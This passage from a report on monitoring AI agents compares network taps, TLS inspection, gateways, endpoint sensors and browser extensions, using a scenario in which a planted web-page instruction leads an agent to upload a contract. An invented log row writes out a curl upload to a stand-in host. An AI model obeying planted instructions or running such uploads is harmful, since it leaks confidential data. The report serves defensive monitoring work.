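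Canale and Soulis also point out that an approved application and an unapproved script look the same on the network if they call the same provider. They built a detector that runs on devices, so they have an interest in this comparison, but the point is correct because a flow record identifies a machine but not the program that made the connection.

The sites a research agent visits can reveal what its user wanted. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025), in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, found that such agents visit 70 to 140 sites for a single query. They had a language model reconstruct the prompt from the site names and the timing of the visits. By their own measure of similarity, it recovered over 73% of what the prompt asked for and the subject knowledge in it. The method still worked when they hid 40% of the visits. It requires an observer who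 can follow the whole session and read the site names, which encrypted DNS or a virtual private network would hide.

The size and timing of packets carry information too. Hosted models commonly send a reply in small pieces as they generate it, so packet sizes partly reflect the length of the words, and packet timing partly reflects the speed of the model. An agent's traffic also pauses while a tool runs and comes in bursts when results arrive.

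Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025), in *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, tested whether these patterns identify particular agents. They recorded encrypted traffic between users and 50 hosted agents, divided it into short time slices, and trained a neural network on the number of packets and bytes in each slice. The network identified the correct agent 86.7% of the time and the correct kind of behaviour, out of five, 94.1% of the time. It did somewhat worse when the traffic included agents that were not in its training data. Zhang and colleagues wrote their prompts to make each agent perform its main function, but real users also ask unrelated questions. They acknowledge that an email-writing agent produces no distinctive pattern when asked a casual health question.

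Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026) tried to infer the task of a team of agents from its encrypted exchanges with a model, in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*. With ten kinds of task, such as coding and contract analysis, their classifier was right about 85% of the time, against 10% for guessing. With traffic from only one agent, its accuracy was 66.5% or 78%, depending on how the team was organised. Accuracy fell from 83% to 52% when they trained the classifier on teams organised one way and tested it on teams organised the other way.

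These numbers probably make the method look better than it is. Although the title refers to cloud services, Pouryousef and colleagues ran the models on their own hardware, and every team used the same small model. Every recording also belonged to one of the ten categories, whereas most traffic on a company network would belong to none of them.

The test closest to that situation is in *Whisper Leak*, by two Microsoft researchers (McDonald and Bar Or, 2025). They tried to pick out conversations about one sensitive topic, such as money laundering, when unrelated conversations outnumbered them by up to 10,000 to one. For many of the 28 models tested, they could do this with no false alarms, but they found only 5% to 20% of the conversations on the topic. That might be enough for a spy, but a company that needs to know everything its agents did could not use a method that misses at least four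 in five conversations.

All four papers treat traffic analysis as an attack on privacy, and none covers detecting an agent that sends a file to the wrong place. The ordinary flow record is already quite good for that. In the example, it shows 1.8 megabytes going to an address that no one else at the company may ever have contacted. Analysing the traffic's shape would add a guess about which agent was involved, but only after someone had trained the classifier on each agent.

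### TLS inspection

To learn what the 1.8 megabytes contained, the company has to decrypt the connection. When a program connects to a site over TLS, the site sends a certificate, a file that links the site's name to an encryption key. A certificate authority signs the certificate, and every device has a list of the authorities it trusts. To inspect TLS traffic, the organisation adds itself to that list.

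1. The organisation creates its own certificate authority and installs the authority's certificate on each device it manages.
2. It routes the devices' traffic through a proxy.
3. A program on the laptop tries to connect to an outside site. The proxy answers in the site's place and opens its own TLS connection to the real site.
4. The proxy creates a new certificate in the site's name, signs it with the organisation's authority and presents it to the program.
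5. The program finds the authority on the device's list and accepts the certificate.
6. The program encrypts its request with keys it shares with the proxy. The proxy decrypts the request, logs or checks it, and encrypts it again for the real site. The reply comes back the same way.

The data is readable inside the proxy, so the proxy is itself a security risk. What it logs depends on the product and its settings. A log entry for step 5, with invented values, could look like this.

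| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Time | 3 November 2026, 14:36:41 UTC |
| Device and user | 10.20.4.76; A. Rossi, from the proxy's sign-in |
| Request | POST (send data) to files.dropsite.example, path /upload |
| Program, as stated in the request | curl/8.7.1 |
| Content | "Supply agreement.pdf", 1.8 megabytes |
| Policy check | Matches a document marked confidential |
| Response | 200 (success) |

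The company now knows which contract left. The program name is a useful clue because few lawyers use command-line tools like curl, but it isn't proof, since a program can put any name in that field. The company also can't tell from the entry whether the agent or the employee ran the command.

Step 4 is harder to interpret. The email's recipient and text pass through the proxy in whatever format the webmail site uses, so the inspection product must know that format to extract them. Even then, the email looks as if the employee sent it.

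Decryption also lets an organisation distinguish between different uses of the same destination. *Holding Agents Accountable* cites a case in which OpenAI's agents used a package repository, provided for downloading software, to exchange messages between separate tasks. A list of permitted destinations would not have caught this, because the repository was on the list. Catching it requires a record of the operation, such as a read or a write, and its result. The number of bytes sent in a flow record might suggest a write, but a decrypted request shows the operation itself.

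### Gateways for model requests and MCP calls

An inspection proxy handles whatever traffic reaches it, but much of that traffic is in formats it can't interpret. A gateway works with the structure of prompts and tool calls, though only for traffic that harnesses send to it. To use a model gateway, the company sets the harness to send requests to the gateway's address instead of the provider's. According to Canale and Soulis, this takes one setting in most harnesses. The gateway then logs each request and passes it on.

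Oso, which sells such a gateway, records the parameters and response of each tool call along with the prompts and replies, and links each session to a user, a group and a device. A record of step 5 in this style, again with invented values, might be:

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Time | 3 November 2026, 14:36:39 UTC |
| User, device, agent | A. Rossi; laptop-0417; doc-agent-12, session 88 |
| Prompt | The conversation so far, including contract text and the web page with the planted instruction |
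| Reply | Tool call to "shell": upload "Supply agreement.pdf" to files.dropsite.example |
| Tool response, from the next request | "Upload complete" |

The gateway log explains more than any other record on this route because it names the agent and contains the text that misled it, which neither the flow record nor the decrypted upload includes. But the gateway sits between the harness and the model, so it logs the model's request for an upload and the harness's later report that the upload worked, not the upload itself, which takes a different path. Oso tells customers that "nothing slips through" because it records commands as well as MCP calls. That may be true of the calls the model makes, but it cannot cover the programs that a script then starts.

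An MCP gateway sits between the harness and its tools, so it logs the calls the harness actually makes and the answers that come back. Suppose the company had connected its mail service through MCP, so that the agent did not need webmail. The request in step 4 would then contain something like this:

```
{"jsonrpc":"2.0", "id":17, "method":"tools/call",
 "params":{"name":"send_email",
  "arguments":{"to":"counsel@lawfirm.example",
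   "subject":"Contract summary", "body":"..."}}}
```

When an agent sends email through a mail tool, the recipient is a labelled field, so nobody has to work it out from a webmail site's private format. The gateway can also record the time, which agent sent the email and the mail service's reply. A company that wants good records of its agents' emails therefore has a reason to give the agents a mail tool and keep them out of webmail.

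Not all MCP servers communicate over a network, because the standard also lets a harness run a server on the same machine and exchange messages with it directly. Canale and Soulis cite a vendor's survey of nearly 10,000 developer environments in which about half the developers had at least one MCP server installed. A gateway elsewhere on the network records calls to a local server only if the company moves the server behind the gateway or installs software on the developer's machine to relay the messages.

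### Traffic that this route misses

Some programs use certificate pinning, which means they accept only specific certificates set in advance, and they reject the one the proxy presents. The organisation then has to block the program or exempt it from inspection, in which case it sees only the program's flow and DNS records. Programs that keep their own list of trusted authorities also reject the proxy's certificate, but only until an administrator adds the organisation's certificate to that list.

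Encrypted Client Hello (ECH), a recent addition to TLS, hides the site name that a tap could otherwise read at the start of a connection. The tap sees a public name instead, which many sites may share. Canale and Soulis list this as a structural limit of network monitoring. ECH affects taps much more than inspection proxies. Under the IETF's *TLS Encrypted Client Hello*, a proxy that does not support ECH answers under the public name. If the program accepts the organisation's certificate for that name, it can retry without ECH. Otherwise the connection may fail, which at least alerts the organisation to a problem. The standard also mentions that companies can turn ECH off by policy on devices they manage, provided the programs honour the setting.

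Laptops also connect from homes and hotels, where their traffic bypasses the company's taps and proxies unless software on the laptop redirects it. That software works, but the company has to install it on every laptop, as it does the certificate for TLS inspection. This route therefore requires installing nothing in the agent, but it avoids installing anything on the device only when monitoring is passive and the device is on the company's own network.

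If the model runs on the laptop itself, there is no traffic with a model provider to inspect. Programs such as Ollama serve a model at an address inside the machine, so the prompts never leave it. The agent would still have to use the network to send the email and upload the contract.

Agents that run in a provider's cloud cause the opposite problem, because what they send to outsiders never crosses the company's network. Equipment on that network can record only the traffic between the employee's computer and the provider. Canale and Soulis give the example of GitHub's cloud coding agent, which edits files and runs tests in a cloud environment rather than on the developer's machine. An organisation that uses such agents depends on the provider's records.

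The partial answer from advocates of gateways is to block direct connections so that agents can reach models and tools only through the gateway. This is realistic on company servers, because engineers can put them on a network with no other way out. Anything an agent tries to send elsewhere then fails and appears in the firewall's log.

Laptops are harder to restrict because people need the open web for work. The company can block the known model providers and allow the gateway, but someone has to keep the list of providers current, and the block has to work on every network the laptop joins. The harness must also let the customer change the address it connects to. Oso's gateway works only with agents that allow this, and Canale and Soulis list several AI code editors that connect to their maker's own servers. For those, the company would have to rely on TLS inspection or choose a different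 product. Blocking doesn't cover hosted agents or local models, though a company can forbid them.

### The six steps on the network

The table applies when the harness runs on the laptop, the laptop is on the company's network, and every program accepts the company's certificate. The "With decryption" column covers TLS inspection of all traffic, including traffic with the model provider. A model gateway alone would supply the parts of that column that come from prompts and replies.

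| Step | Without decryption | With decryption |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Exchange with the model | The provider's address, with times and volumes | Full prompts and replies, including contract text |
| 2. Reading the contracts | Nothing | Any contract text that the harness puts in a prompt, but not the act of reading |
| 3. Writing and running the script | Nothing, unless the script uses the network | The script and what it printed, but not the programs it started |
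| 4. Email to counsel | A connection to the mail service and its approximate size | Recipient and text, if the product can interpret the webmail format |
| 5. Web page and upload | Both destinations, with times and volumes | The planted text, the file and the server's response |
| 6. Scheduled job | Nothing, unless the next day's run uses the network | The command that created the job, but not the next day's run unless it uses the network |

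Decryption adds entries for steps 2, 3 and 6 only because the harness exchanges commands and results with a model outside the laptop. If the model ran locally, those three entries would be empty even with decryption, but the records of the email and the upload would stay the same.

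## The case for software on the device

Much of the activity that a network tap misses in the example happens on the laptop: the file reads, the programs that the script starts, and the scheduled job. An endpoint sensor runs on the same machine, so it can record these events even if nothing crosses a network and the agent never reports them.

Hand gives the fullest argument for putting monitoring software on the device. The harness, the browser and any local model or MCP server all run there, so the software can record which files an agent opens, which programs it starts and where those programs connect. It can also read prompts before they leave the device and list the MCP servers in an agent's settings, including those that never use the network.

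Hand also argues that a sensor on the device makes incidents easier to investigate. A network log records prompts and, separately, connections; a browser extension records events in a tab; and an operating system's audit log records processes and files without context. Matching the three during an incident is, in his words, "a research project" for which most teams have no time. A sensor collects all these events on one machine, in order and under one user account.

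Hand, whose company sells such a sensor, slightly overstates what it can do. Putting events in time order doesn't establish which caused which. If the employee and two agents are working at once, their events are mixed together, and the sensor still has to determine which belong together.

Hand concedes that network monitoring is a defensible choice for a company that mainly wants to see the prompts going to public AI providers and wants to start quickly. He also concedes that managed browsers can remove sensitive fields from a prompt before the employee submits it, or stop someone pasting certain data into a chatbot. To use sensors, a company has to install one on every device it wants to observe. Hand thinks this is worth the trouble wherever agents do real work, but he accepts that a partial view may be enough for some companies.

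SentinelOne, which also sells endpoint sensors, makes a similar case. In *SentinelOne’s Chris Corde On Why Traditional EDR Is ‘Flying Blind’* (Alspach, 2026), its product chief says that network gateways miss most of what agents do, especially to files. He is right about the files. But Claude's models run on remote servers, so prompts from a laptop still cross the network, contrary to his claim that Claude on a laptop effectively has its model built in.

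### How a sensor collects events

An ordinary program cannot open a file, start another program or connect to a network by itself. It has to send a request, known as a system call, to the kernel, the core of the operating system. A script that an agent wrote a minute ago makes the same system calls as any other program, so a sensor that takes its events from the kernel doesn't need a list of the programs the agent will use.

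On Windows, sensors have traditionally used drivers, which run inside the kernel. A driver can register a routine that Windows calls whenever a process starts or exits, as Microsoft's *PsSetCreateProcessNotifyRoutineEx function (ntddk.h)* explains. The routine runs in the context of the thread that created the process, which lets the sensor build the process lineage, a record of which program started which. For file events, sensors use another kind of driver called a minifilter, according to Elastic's *macOS Windows what kernels tell you about security events part 2*. They observe network connections through a separate interface, the Windows Filtering Platform.

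Windows also has a general logging system, Event Tracing for Windows. Uhlmann and Bousseaden, who work for the endpoint security vendor Elastic, report that Microsoft uses it to provide near real-time records of a few security-relevant system calls. These records let a sensor log the calls but not block them.

A faulty kernel driver can crash the whole machine, so Microsoft wants security products to depend less on the kernel. Microsoft's *The Windows Resiliency Initiative* (2025) announced a private preview of a platform that lets these products run outside the kernel, as ordinary applications do.

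Apple has already made that move on the Mac. A sensor registers with an interface called Endpoint Security, which notifies it of events after they happen or lets it authorise them beforehand, according to Apple's *Endpoint Security*. The events include starting a program and opening or renaming a file. Network traffic comes through a different framework, the Network Extension, which WithSecure's *MacOS Endpoint Security Framework (ESF)* lists separately. A Mac sensor needs both frameworks to record the upload in step 5 and the program that made it.

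A Mac sensor normally needs administrator rights and a special privacy approval, because it can observe every user's files. In macOS 27, Apple added a narrower option that lets a program ask for events from only itself and its descendants (the processes it starts, the processes those start, and so on). Apple's *es_new_descendants_client(_:_:)* says this requires neither the rights nor the approval. Apple engineers name agents as the main intended use in their replies to a developer in *Is there some tutorial for the new `es_new_descendants_client` function?*. A harness could, for instance, ask the user to approve each operation before macOS allows it.

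The narrower option would miss some of the activity in the example. The operating system starts the scheduled job in step 6, so the job does not descend from the harness, and neither does a browser that the employee opened that morning. Also, if the harness itself collects the events, the record is not independent.

### eBPF and text inside encrypted connections

Linux has a more flexible mechanism called eBPF, which runs small programs inside the kernel without any change to the kernel's own code. Suppose a sensor needs to record every file that any process opens. Going by the *eBPF Documentation*, it would work as follows:

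1. The sensor's developers write a short program that notes the file's name and the process that opened it.
2. The sensor loads the program into the kernel. By default, only software with special privileges can do this.
3. A part of the kernel called the verifier checks the program. It rejects any program that might never finish, that reads memory outside its limits, or that is too large or complex.
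4. The kernel translates the program into machine code and attaches it to a chosen point, in this case the system call that opens files.
5. Whenever a process reaches that point, the program runs and puts its notes in a shared data structure, where the sensor collects them.

The eBPF verifier checks only that a program is safe to run. A program that copies confidential text can pass as easily as one that counts files, so a company still has to trust whoever supplied the sensor.

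eBPF programs can also attach to functions inside ordinary applications, through what Linux calls a user probe. This gives the sensor a way to read encrypted traffic without decrypting it. Most programs leave encryption to a TLS library such as OpenSSL. To send data, the program passes readable text to the library's `SSL_write` function, which encrypts it. To receive data, the program calls `SSL_read`, which returns the decrypted text. A probe on `SSL_write` copies the text before encryption, and a probe on `SSL_read` copies it after decryption. In step 1, these copies would contain the prompt and the model's reply.

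Unlike TLS inspection, this method does not alter the connection. The program receives the site's real certificate, so the organisation does not need to install its own, and certificate pinning does not interfere. Bernosky (2025), in *Are You Watching What's Leaving Your Network?*, adds that inspection proxies slow traffic and can block it when they fail. His employer, Qpoint, offers a tool based on these probes, which he presents as a complete view of AI traffic from a company's servers.

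A probe works only on a library it was built for. The set of probes tested in *Connection Escrow* (2026) covers OpenSSL and Go's TLS library, but Rustls, a library written in Rust, would need another set. A probe can also fail when a program contains its own copy of a library without the labels the probe uses to find the right function.

The probes in *Connection Escrow* also copy at most the first 16 kilobytes of each write, while *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) sets its limit at about 128 kilobytes. A prompt containing 14 contracts could easily exceed either limit, leaving an investigator with only part of it.

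### Why an agent looks like any other program

Companies have used endpoint sensors for years to find malicious software. The usual name for these products is endpoint detection and response (EDR). For the upload in step 5, such a product might record the following, with invented values:

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Time | 3 November 2026, 14:36:40 UTC |
| Device and user | laptop-0417; A. Rossi |
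| Program | curl |
| Command | `curl -F "file=@Supply agreement.pdf" https://files.dropsite.example/upload` |
| Started by | bash (a command shell), which doc-agent started |
| Connection | 203.0.113.50, port 443 |

Endpoint software's record of an upload is much better than the network's flow record of it, because it shows the file, the destination and the program without the company having to decrypt anything.

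But the record doesn't identify doc-agent as an AI agent, only as a program running under A. Rossi's account. The program's name is a clue, but many harnesses run inside general-purpose software such as Node.js or Python, and then the record may show only the name of that software. The upload may not raise an alert either, because EDR products look for signs of an attack and developers often use curl for ordinary work. *The next frontier in endpoint security* (Shteinberg, 2026), a Microsoft post announcing the company's own remedy, describes local agents as running like "ordinary processes", with little of the context that security teams need.

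Corde makes the stronger claim that traditional EDR cannot see these agents at all. That is wrong for step 5, where EDR records the event without a label or an explanation. The claim is closer to the truth for tools built into the harness. If the harness opens a contract itself, the sensor can record that the harness read a file, but not which tool call led to the read.

Sensor makers can supply the label by programming their products to recognise known harnesses. Microsoft's Defender, for example, finds more than 20 kinds of local agent, according to Shteinberg. It also lists the MCP servers these agents connect to and shows whether a harness approves tool calls automatically. This helps a company find agents that are missing from its register.

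However, the inventory is coarse. Microsoft counts each combination of user, device and type of agent once, so Claude Code running in 15 project folders is a single entry. The inventory would probably also omit a script that an employee wrote to call a model.

Once a sensor recognises the harness, it can use process lineage to mark every program descended from the harness as the agent's. This works well for step 3, in which the script starts several other programs, but fails for the scheduled job because its parent is the operating system's scheduler.

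### Microsoft Defender and local agents

In June 2026 Microsoft began a preview of AI agent runtime protection, which extends a sensor that many companies already have to cover the agent's own prompts and tool calls. It relies on the harness's hooks, which Microsoft says run when the user submits a prompt, before a tool call, and after the tool returns its result.

The third point matters most in step 5, when the web page with the planted instruction reaches the harness as the result of a tool call and Defender scans it. If Defender recognises the instruction and is in "block" mode, it stops the agent from acting on it, notifies the employee and sends the security team an alert. In "audit" mode, it sends the alert but lets the agent continue. The timing matters, as pisinger explains in *Stopping Prompt Injection at the Endpoint*, because the check comes before a risky action turns into a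 normal operating system event, which would be hard for a sensor to distinguish from legitimate work.

These scans and alerts are not a log of what the agent did. Microsoft describes the scans as quick checks at set points rather than continuous monitoring, and Defender raises alerts only when it detects something. It would raise no prompt-injection alert if it failed to recognise the planted text, and none for the email to counsel, which had nothing wrong with it. For a record of those steps, the company would have to rely on the sensor's ordinary events.

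The hooks also exist only where the maker of the harness has provided them, so this is partly telemetry from the agent software. For some agents without hooks, Defender instead inspects, on the device, the traffic between the agent and its model. According to Appel's *Configure AI agent runtime protection preview with Microsoft Defender for Endpoint*, this inspection doesn't cover agents that use certificate pinning or HTTP/3, the newest version of HTTP.

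The list of supported agents has grown since June, when it contained only Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI. Appel's list for hooks adds the GitHub Copilot app, the Code mode of Claude Desktop, and the Copilot and Claude Code extensions for the VS Code editor. His list for network inspection contains OpenClaw, Ollama Desktop, ChatGPT Classic and the chat mode of ChatGPT Desktop. *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR* (Scalzi, 2026) also includes OpenAI's Codex CLI among the agents with hooks, but Appel's list does not. A company should therefore check Microsoft's current list for each agent it uses.

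It should also check that both kinds of inspection are on. During the preview, Microsoft's standard management profile switched on only the hooks, and network inspection needed a separate script. An administrator who applied only the profile would have had no runtime protection for OpenClaw.

When Scalzi wrote on 3 November, the feature was available only in Defender's beta channel, and he warned readers to try it on a few devices first. Later that month, at its Ignite conference, Microsoft announced that runtime protection was generally available on Windows, though with an asterisk after the phrase. The announcement in Microsoft's *defender news* lists Claude Code, GitHub Copilot CLI, OpenClaw and ChatGPT Desktop's chat mode among the supported agents.

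Microsoft's setup instructions from June required a Windows device enrolled in Defender, with Microsoft's own antivirus in active mode. This initially excluded companies that used another maker's antivirus as their main one.

### Where sensors have no coverage

An endpoint sensor records activity only on machines where it is installed. A contractor's laptop or an employee's home computer may run agents with access to company accounts, and the company would have to learn about those agents from the services they use.

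Agents that run in a provider's cloud are a larger gap, and probably a growing one. A customer cannot install a sensor on Anthropic's servers, so with Claude Cowork a sensor on the laptop would record only the traffic to Anthropic and the local files that Cowork opened through its app. According to Scalzi, even Microsoft Defender gets its data about agents built in services such as Copilot Studio and Microsoft Foundry from those services, not from the device. A company can still put sensors on cloud servers that it rents and manages itself.

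Some agents run on the laptop but inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own kernel. Corde gives Claude's desktop software as an example. Programs inside the virtual machine make their system calls to its kernel, not the laptop's, so the sensor on the laptop may record one large process, some network traffic and shared files, but not the individual programs. To record those, the company needs another sensor inside the virtual machine. A sandbox that only restricts a process running on the laptop's own kernel is less of an obstacle to the laptop's sensor.

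Endpoint coverage can arrive slowly, as it has for Windows Subsystem for Linux, which lets developers run Linux programs on a Windows laptop. According to Releasebot's *Microsoft Defender for Endpoint Updates & Release Notes* (2026), Defender's October 2026 release notes list discovery of local agents on Windows and macOS, but discovery inside the subsystem was still in preview. Containers in the subsystem need a separate plug-in, which was also in preview.

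The sandbox can sometimes keep its own record. In October 2026 Microsoft released Execution Containers, which limit the files, applications and networks that an agent on Windows 11 can reach. According to Exame's *Microsoft traz novas ferramentas de IA para o Windows* (2026), one mode blocks forbidden operations and logs the attempts, and another logs them without blocking them. Neither log, as Exame describes them, includes operations that the rules allow, so the upload in step 5 might not appear if the agent may use the web freely. Microsoft has also postponed the controls that would separate an agent's activity from the employee's.

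Coverage also differs between operating systems, even within one product. Microsoft announced general availability of runtime protection only for Windows, and Defender's support for Linux desktops dates from December 2026. A company whose developers use Windows, macOS and Linux could get three different records of the same task from a single product.

A sensor may also receive an event and not keep it. Uhlmann and Bousseaden describe endpoint telemetry as a balance between completeness and cost. Computers open files constantly, so products may keep only some file-open events. A company that wants to know which contracts an agent read in step 2 should test in advance whether its product keeps those events.

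Finally, the operating system's events do not include the instruction behind an action. The record of the upload shows that doc-agent started a shell and the shell started curl. It doesn't show that the instruction came from a web page, which is what the company most needs to know about step 5. A TLS probe or a hook can supply the text, but someone still has to connect that text to the right process. Zheng et al. and Bao et al. have both built tools to do this.

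### The six steps on the device

The table applies when the harness runs directly on a managed laptop and the sensor keeps its file events. The last column assumes a product that also stores the text from TLS probes or harness hooks. A product that only raises alerts would supply less information.

| Step | Process, file and network events | With text from probes or hooks |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Exchange with the model | The harness's connections to the provider | Prompts and replies, up to any limit on length |
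| 2. Reading the contracts | The files opened, and by which program | The tool calls that asked for them, and any contract text in a prompt |
| 3. Writing and running the script | The script, the programs it started and the files they opened | The model's request to write and run it, and what it printed |
| 4. Email to counsel | The browser's connection to the mail service | The agent's instructions to the browser, and the email itself if a probe covers the browser |
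| 5. Web page and upload | The connections, the upload command and the name of the file | The planted text, and at least part of the file if a probe covers the upload program |
| 6. Scheduled job | The creation of the job, and the next day's run | The request that created the job |

The sensor's clearest advantage over a network tap is in step 6, because it records the next day's run even if the script never goes online. It is weakest in step 4, where it cannot distinguish the agent's email from the employee's own without the added text.

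## The case for browser extensions

An endpoint sensor is weakest in step 4, the email to counsel. The agent writes that email in a web page, as it would update a customer record, pay an invoice or edit a shared document. A browser extension is a program that runs inside the browser and can read such pages after the browser has decrypted them, so it doesn't need TLS inspection. It can also read the text in labelled fields such as "To" and "Subject".

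For step 4, an extension written for the company's webmail site could record the following, with invented values:

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Time | 3 November 2026, 14:32:07 UTC |
| Browser | Chrome on laptop-0417, work profile |
| Page | The compose window at mail.company.example |
| Signed-in account | A. Rossi |
| Form fields | To: counsel@lawfirm.example; subject: "Contract summary"; text of 900 words |
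| Attachments | None |
| Action | Click on "Send" |
| Message on the page afterwards | "Message sent" |

The account used can matter as much as the recipient. Many people keep work and private accounts open on the same file-sharing site, and uploads to both may go to the same network address. The page usually shows which account is active.

The record doesn't show whether A. Rossi or the agent clicked "Send". That is the main weakness of this route.

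### How an extension observes a page

Extensions read pages through content scripts, which are pieces of code that the browser runs inside pages listed by the extension's developer. According to Google's *Content scripts*, a content script in Chrome can read and change everything on the page and pass what it finds to the rest of the extension. It works on the same page content as the page's own code, but its variables are separate.

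To record step 4, an extension could work as follows:

1. The administrator installs the extension, with permission for the webmail site.
2. Someone opens webmail, and Chrome adds the content script to the page, by default at about the time the page finishes loading.
3. The script finds the compose form and waits for a click on "Send".
4. When the click comes, the script copies the recipient, subject and text.
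5. The extension adds the time and the tab, and sends the record to the company's log.

The script's developer has to know the site's layout. After a redesign, the script may find nothing until someone updates it. Some sites put their text editor in a frame (a page within the page), and Chrome runs the script there only if the developer has set it to run in frames.

An extension can also follow the requests a page sends. According to Google's *chrome.webRequest*, Chrome notifies the extension at set stages, starting before the browser opens a connection and ending when the request succeeds or fails. The extension can ask for the data in the request, including form entries. For an ordinary file upload, it receives the file's name but not its contents, so a company that wants the contents needs a content script to read the file on the page. Chrome gives each request an identifier that stays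 the same through every stage. The event times are reliable only relative to each other, so a developer who wants to match them with other logs should add a time from the computer's clock.

These events don't contain the text of the site's responses. Chrome's developer tools can supply it, but only while someone has them open on that tab, according to the documentation for Extension.js, a toolkit for building extensions. In practice, an extension has to use a content script to record what a page showed.

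Other permissions cover narrower activities. theluckystrike's community guide *Chrome Extension Permissions Deep Dive* lists one for monitoring downloads, and Chrome has another for reading the clipboard. Clipboard records are probably more useful for observing people than agents, because an agent can enter text in a field without copying and pasting it.

Administrators can install an extension without asking employees. Under the "force_installed" setting in Google's *Configure ExtensionSettings policy*, Chrome adds the extension automatically and users can't remove it. The policy applies to managed Chrome browsers (those whose settings the company controls) on Windows, Mac and Linux.

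### Observing and blocking under Manifest V3

Manifest V3, Chrome's current rules for extensions, restricts blocking more than observing. Any extension with the right permissions can still receive and log request events, but only an extension an administrator has installed by policy can hold a request while it examines the contents, and then cancel it.

Google's *Replace blocking web request listeners* tells extension developers to write rules in advance, such as "block requests to this site", which Chrome then applies itself. The reason is privacy. According to Google's *chrome.declarativeNetRequest*, the extension can then block a request without seeing its content.

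If a company wants to stop emails to anyone outside an approved list, an extension installed by policy could read the recipient from the outgoing request and cancel the request. If the employee had installed the same extension, it could log the email, but it would have to block requests using rules written in advance, which cannot check the recipient. Its content script could still disable the "Send" button, but this is less dependable because webmail sites often have other ways to send a message. A company would normally install its monitoring extension by policy, so Manifest V3 has little effect on its monitoring.

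According to Extension.js, Firefox differs on both points. It still lets ordinary extensions block requests, but users grant access to sites separately, after installation. The same extension may therefore record less in Firefox until the employee grants that access.

### Managed browsers

A company can also use the monitoring built into a browser made for businesses. Microsoft's *New in Edge for Business* (2026) describes how Purview, Microsoft's data-protection product, analyses prompts and file uploads on common consumer AI sites and audits or blocks the action if it detects sensitive data. This needs no extension, and it works even on devices the company doesn't manage, such as a contractor's laptop with no endpoint sensor, as long as the user signs in to Edge with a work account.

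Microsoft claims that Edge is the only major business browser that both applies data-protection rules to AI and keeps sensitive exchanges within the customer's own cloud environment. Google's Chrome Enterprise Premium also applies data-protection rules to AI. According to *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026), they inspect agents' data flows as they happen and block unauthorised transfers to public AI models. Berschadski manages the product for Google, so both companies are describing their own products.

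Monitoring built by the browser's maker can cover places that an extension can't access, including the browser's own agent, but the customer has less choice over what it records. A data-loss rule is also triggered only by content that it is set up to detect as sensitive, so it could miss the reworded summary in step 4. An extension that logs every email would still record it.

### A person using a chatbot in a tab

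Extensions work best when an employee types questions into a chatbot's website. A content script can record the prompt, the reply, the names of any attached files and the account in use. An extension that relied only on request events would miss messages on some sites, because those sites use a WebSocket, a connection that stays open, and Chrome notifies extensions when the connection opens but not when each message passes over it.

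Oso uses its extension this way for the websites of Claude, ChatGPT and Gemini, and to discover browser-based agents that it does not yet monitor. It uses hooks instead for coding agents that run in a terminal or desktop program.

The employee types the prompt into the chatbot, so there is little doubt about who is clicking. Observation is harder when the chatbot acts as an agent and works elsewhere, such as on its provider's servers, because the tab then contains only the conversation and whatever progress the site displays.

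### An agent inside the browser

Some agents are built into the browser. Google's auto browse carries out tasks in Chrome tabs, and Google has opened it to eligible Workspace users in the United States. In May 2026, Microsoft began a limited preview of a similar feature for Copilot in Edge. Other agents are browser extensions, including Claude in Chrome and OpenAI's ChatGPT extension.

When one of these agents fills in a form, a monitoring extension can record the same fields and requests as it would for a person. The agent's instructions are harder to obtain. Chrome shows an extension a request only if the extension has permission for both the request's source and its destination, and it hides some requests that involve other extensions. A monitoring extension therefore probably can't record the prompts that Claude in Chrome sends to Anthropic, so it would have the email to counsel but not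 the prompt that led to it.

When code on a page triggers a click, the browser marks the event as untrusted, and a content script can read the mark. Ordinary websites and other extensions also trigger such clicks, so the mark is evidence of software but not specifically of an agent.

The absence of the mark is also weak evidence that a person clicked. Chrome has a debugging interface for software developers that can send clicks through the browser's normal input path, and a content script cannot distinguish these from an employee's clicks. An extension can use the interface if it has the "debugger" permission, which Google lists with a warning that it gives access to all the user's data on all websites.

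Chrome has better information about its own agent. Auto browse keeps a work log in the tab, according to Berschadski, and Chrome's history labels the background pages that the agent visited. He presents both as ways for the employee to follow the agent. To tell whether the employee or the agent sent an email, a security team would need the same labels in a central log, for individual actions as well as pages.

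Administrators have more ways to control browser agents than records of what the agents did. In Google's *Gemini in Chrome*, they can turn auto browse on or off and list the sites where it may work. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome admin controls* describes an on/off switch, site lists and, for some customers, permissions by role. According to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*, users can also look up their permission history in the extension. That history can help establish which sites the agent was allowed to use, but not what it did there.

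OpenAI's *Manage browser and computer use in your Enterprise workspace* describes finer permissions, with separate settings for opening a site, uploading to it, downloading from it and using the debugging interface. A company could let the agent read webmail but not attach files. That would narrow an investigation considerably, but it would not show which emails the agent had sent.

Chrome's extension policy can help control unapproved agents. An administrator can block any extension that requires a particular permission, such as "debugger", and Chrome will stop loading copies that employees have already installed. The monitoring extension may need an exception if it uses the same permission.

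### A harness that drives the browser

A harness can also run outside the browser and control it through an automation interface, which software testers use to open pages and press buttons with code. Some harnesses instead move the on-screen pointer and type as a person would.

If the harness uses the employee's own browser, the monitoring extension can record the pages and forms as before. Standard automation tools usually set a flag in the browsers they start, which a content script can read. The flag shows that software is controlling the browser but doesn't identify the agent, and it may be missing if the harness connected to a browser that was already open. A harness that operates the screen sends its input through the operating system, so the flag is normally not set.

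Strac's *AI Agent Monitoring* (2026) describes such a case. Alice, an employee, is signed in to Salesforce, a service for managing customer records. Claude Cowork takes control of her tab and exports a report of 2,310 rows. Salesforce logs the export under Alice's name, with no sign of an agent.

Strac's endpoint sensor records the Cowork process taking control of the tab. Its browser sensor records a tool call to click "Export". The endpoint sensor then records the download, the agent reading the file, and traffic from the agent's process to Anthropic. Strac's software attributes the export to the agent because the activity overlaps by 43 seconds, the tab and account match, and the agent then read the downloaded file.

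The overlap alone would prove little, since Alice could have clicked "Export" while the agent was working. The tool call is much stronger evidence because it is the agent's request for that click. An extension that records only the page would capture the click but not the tool call.

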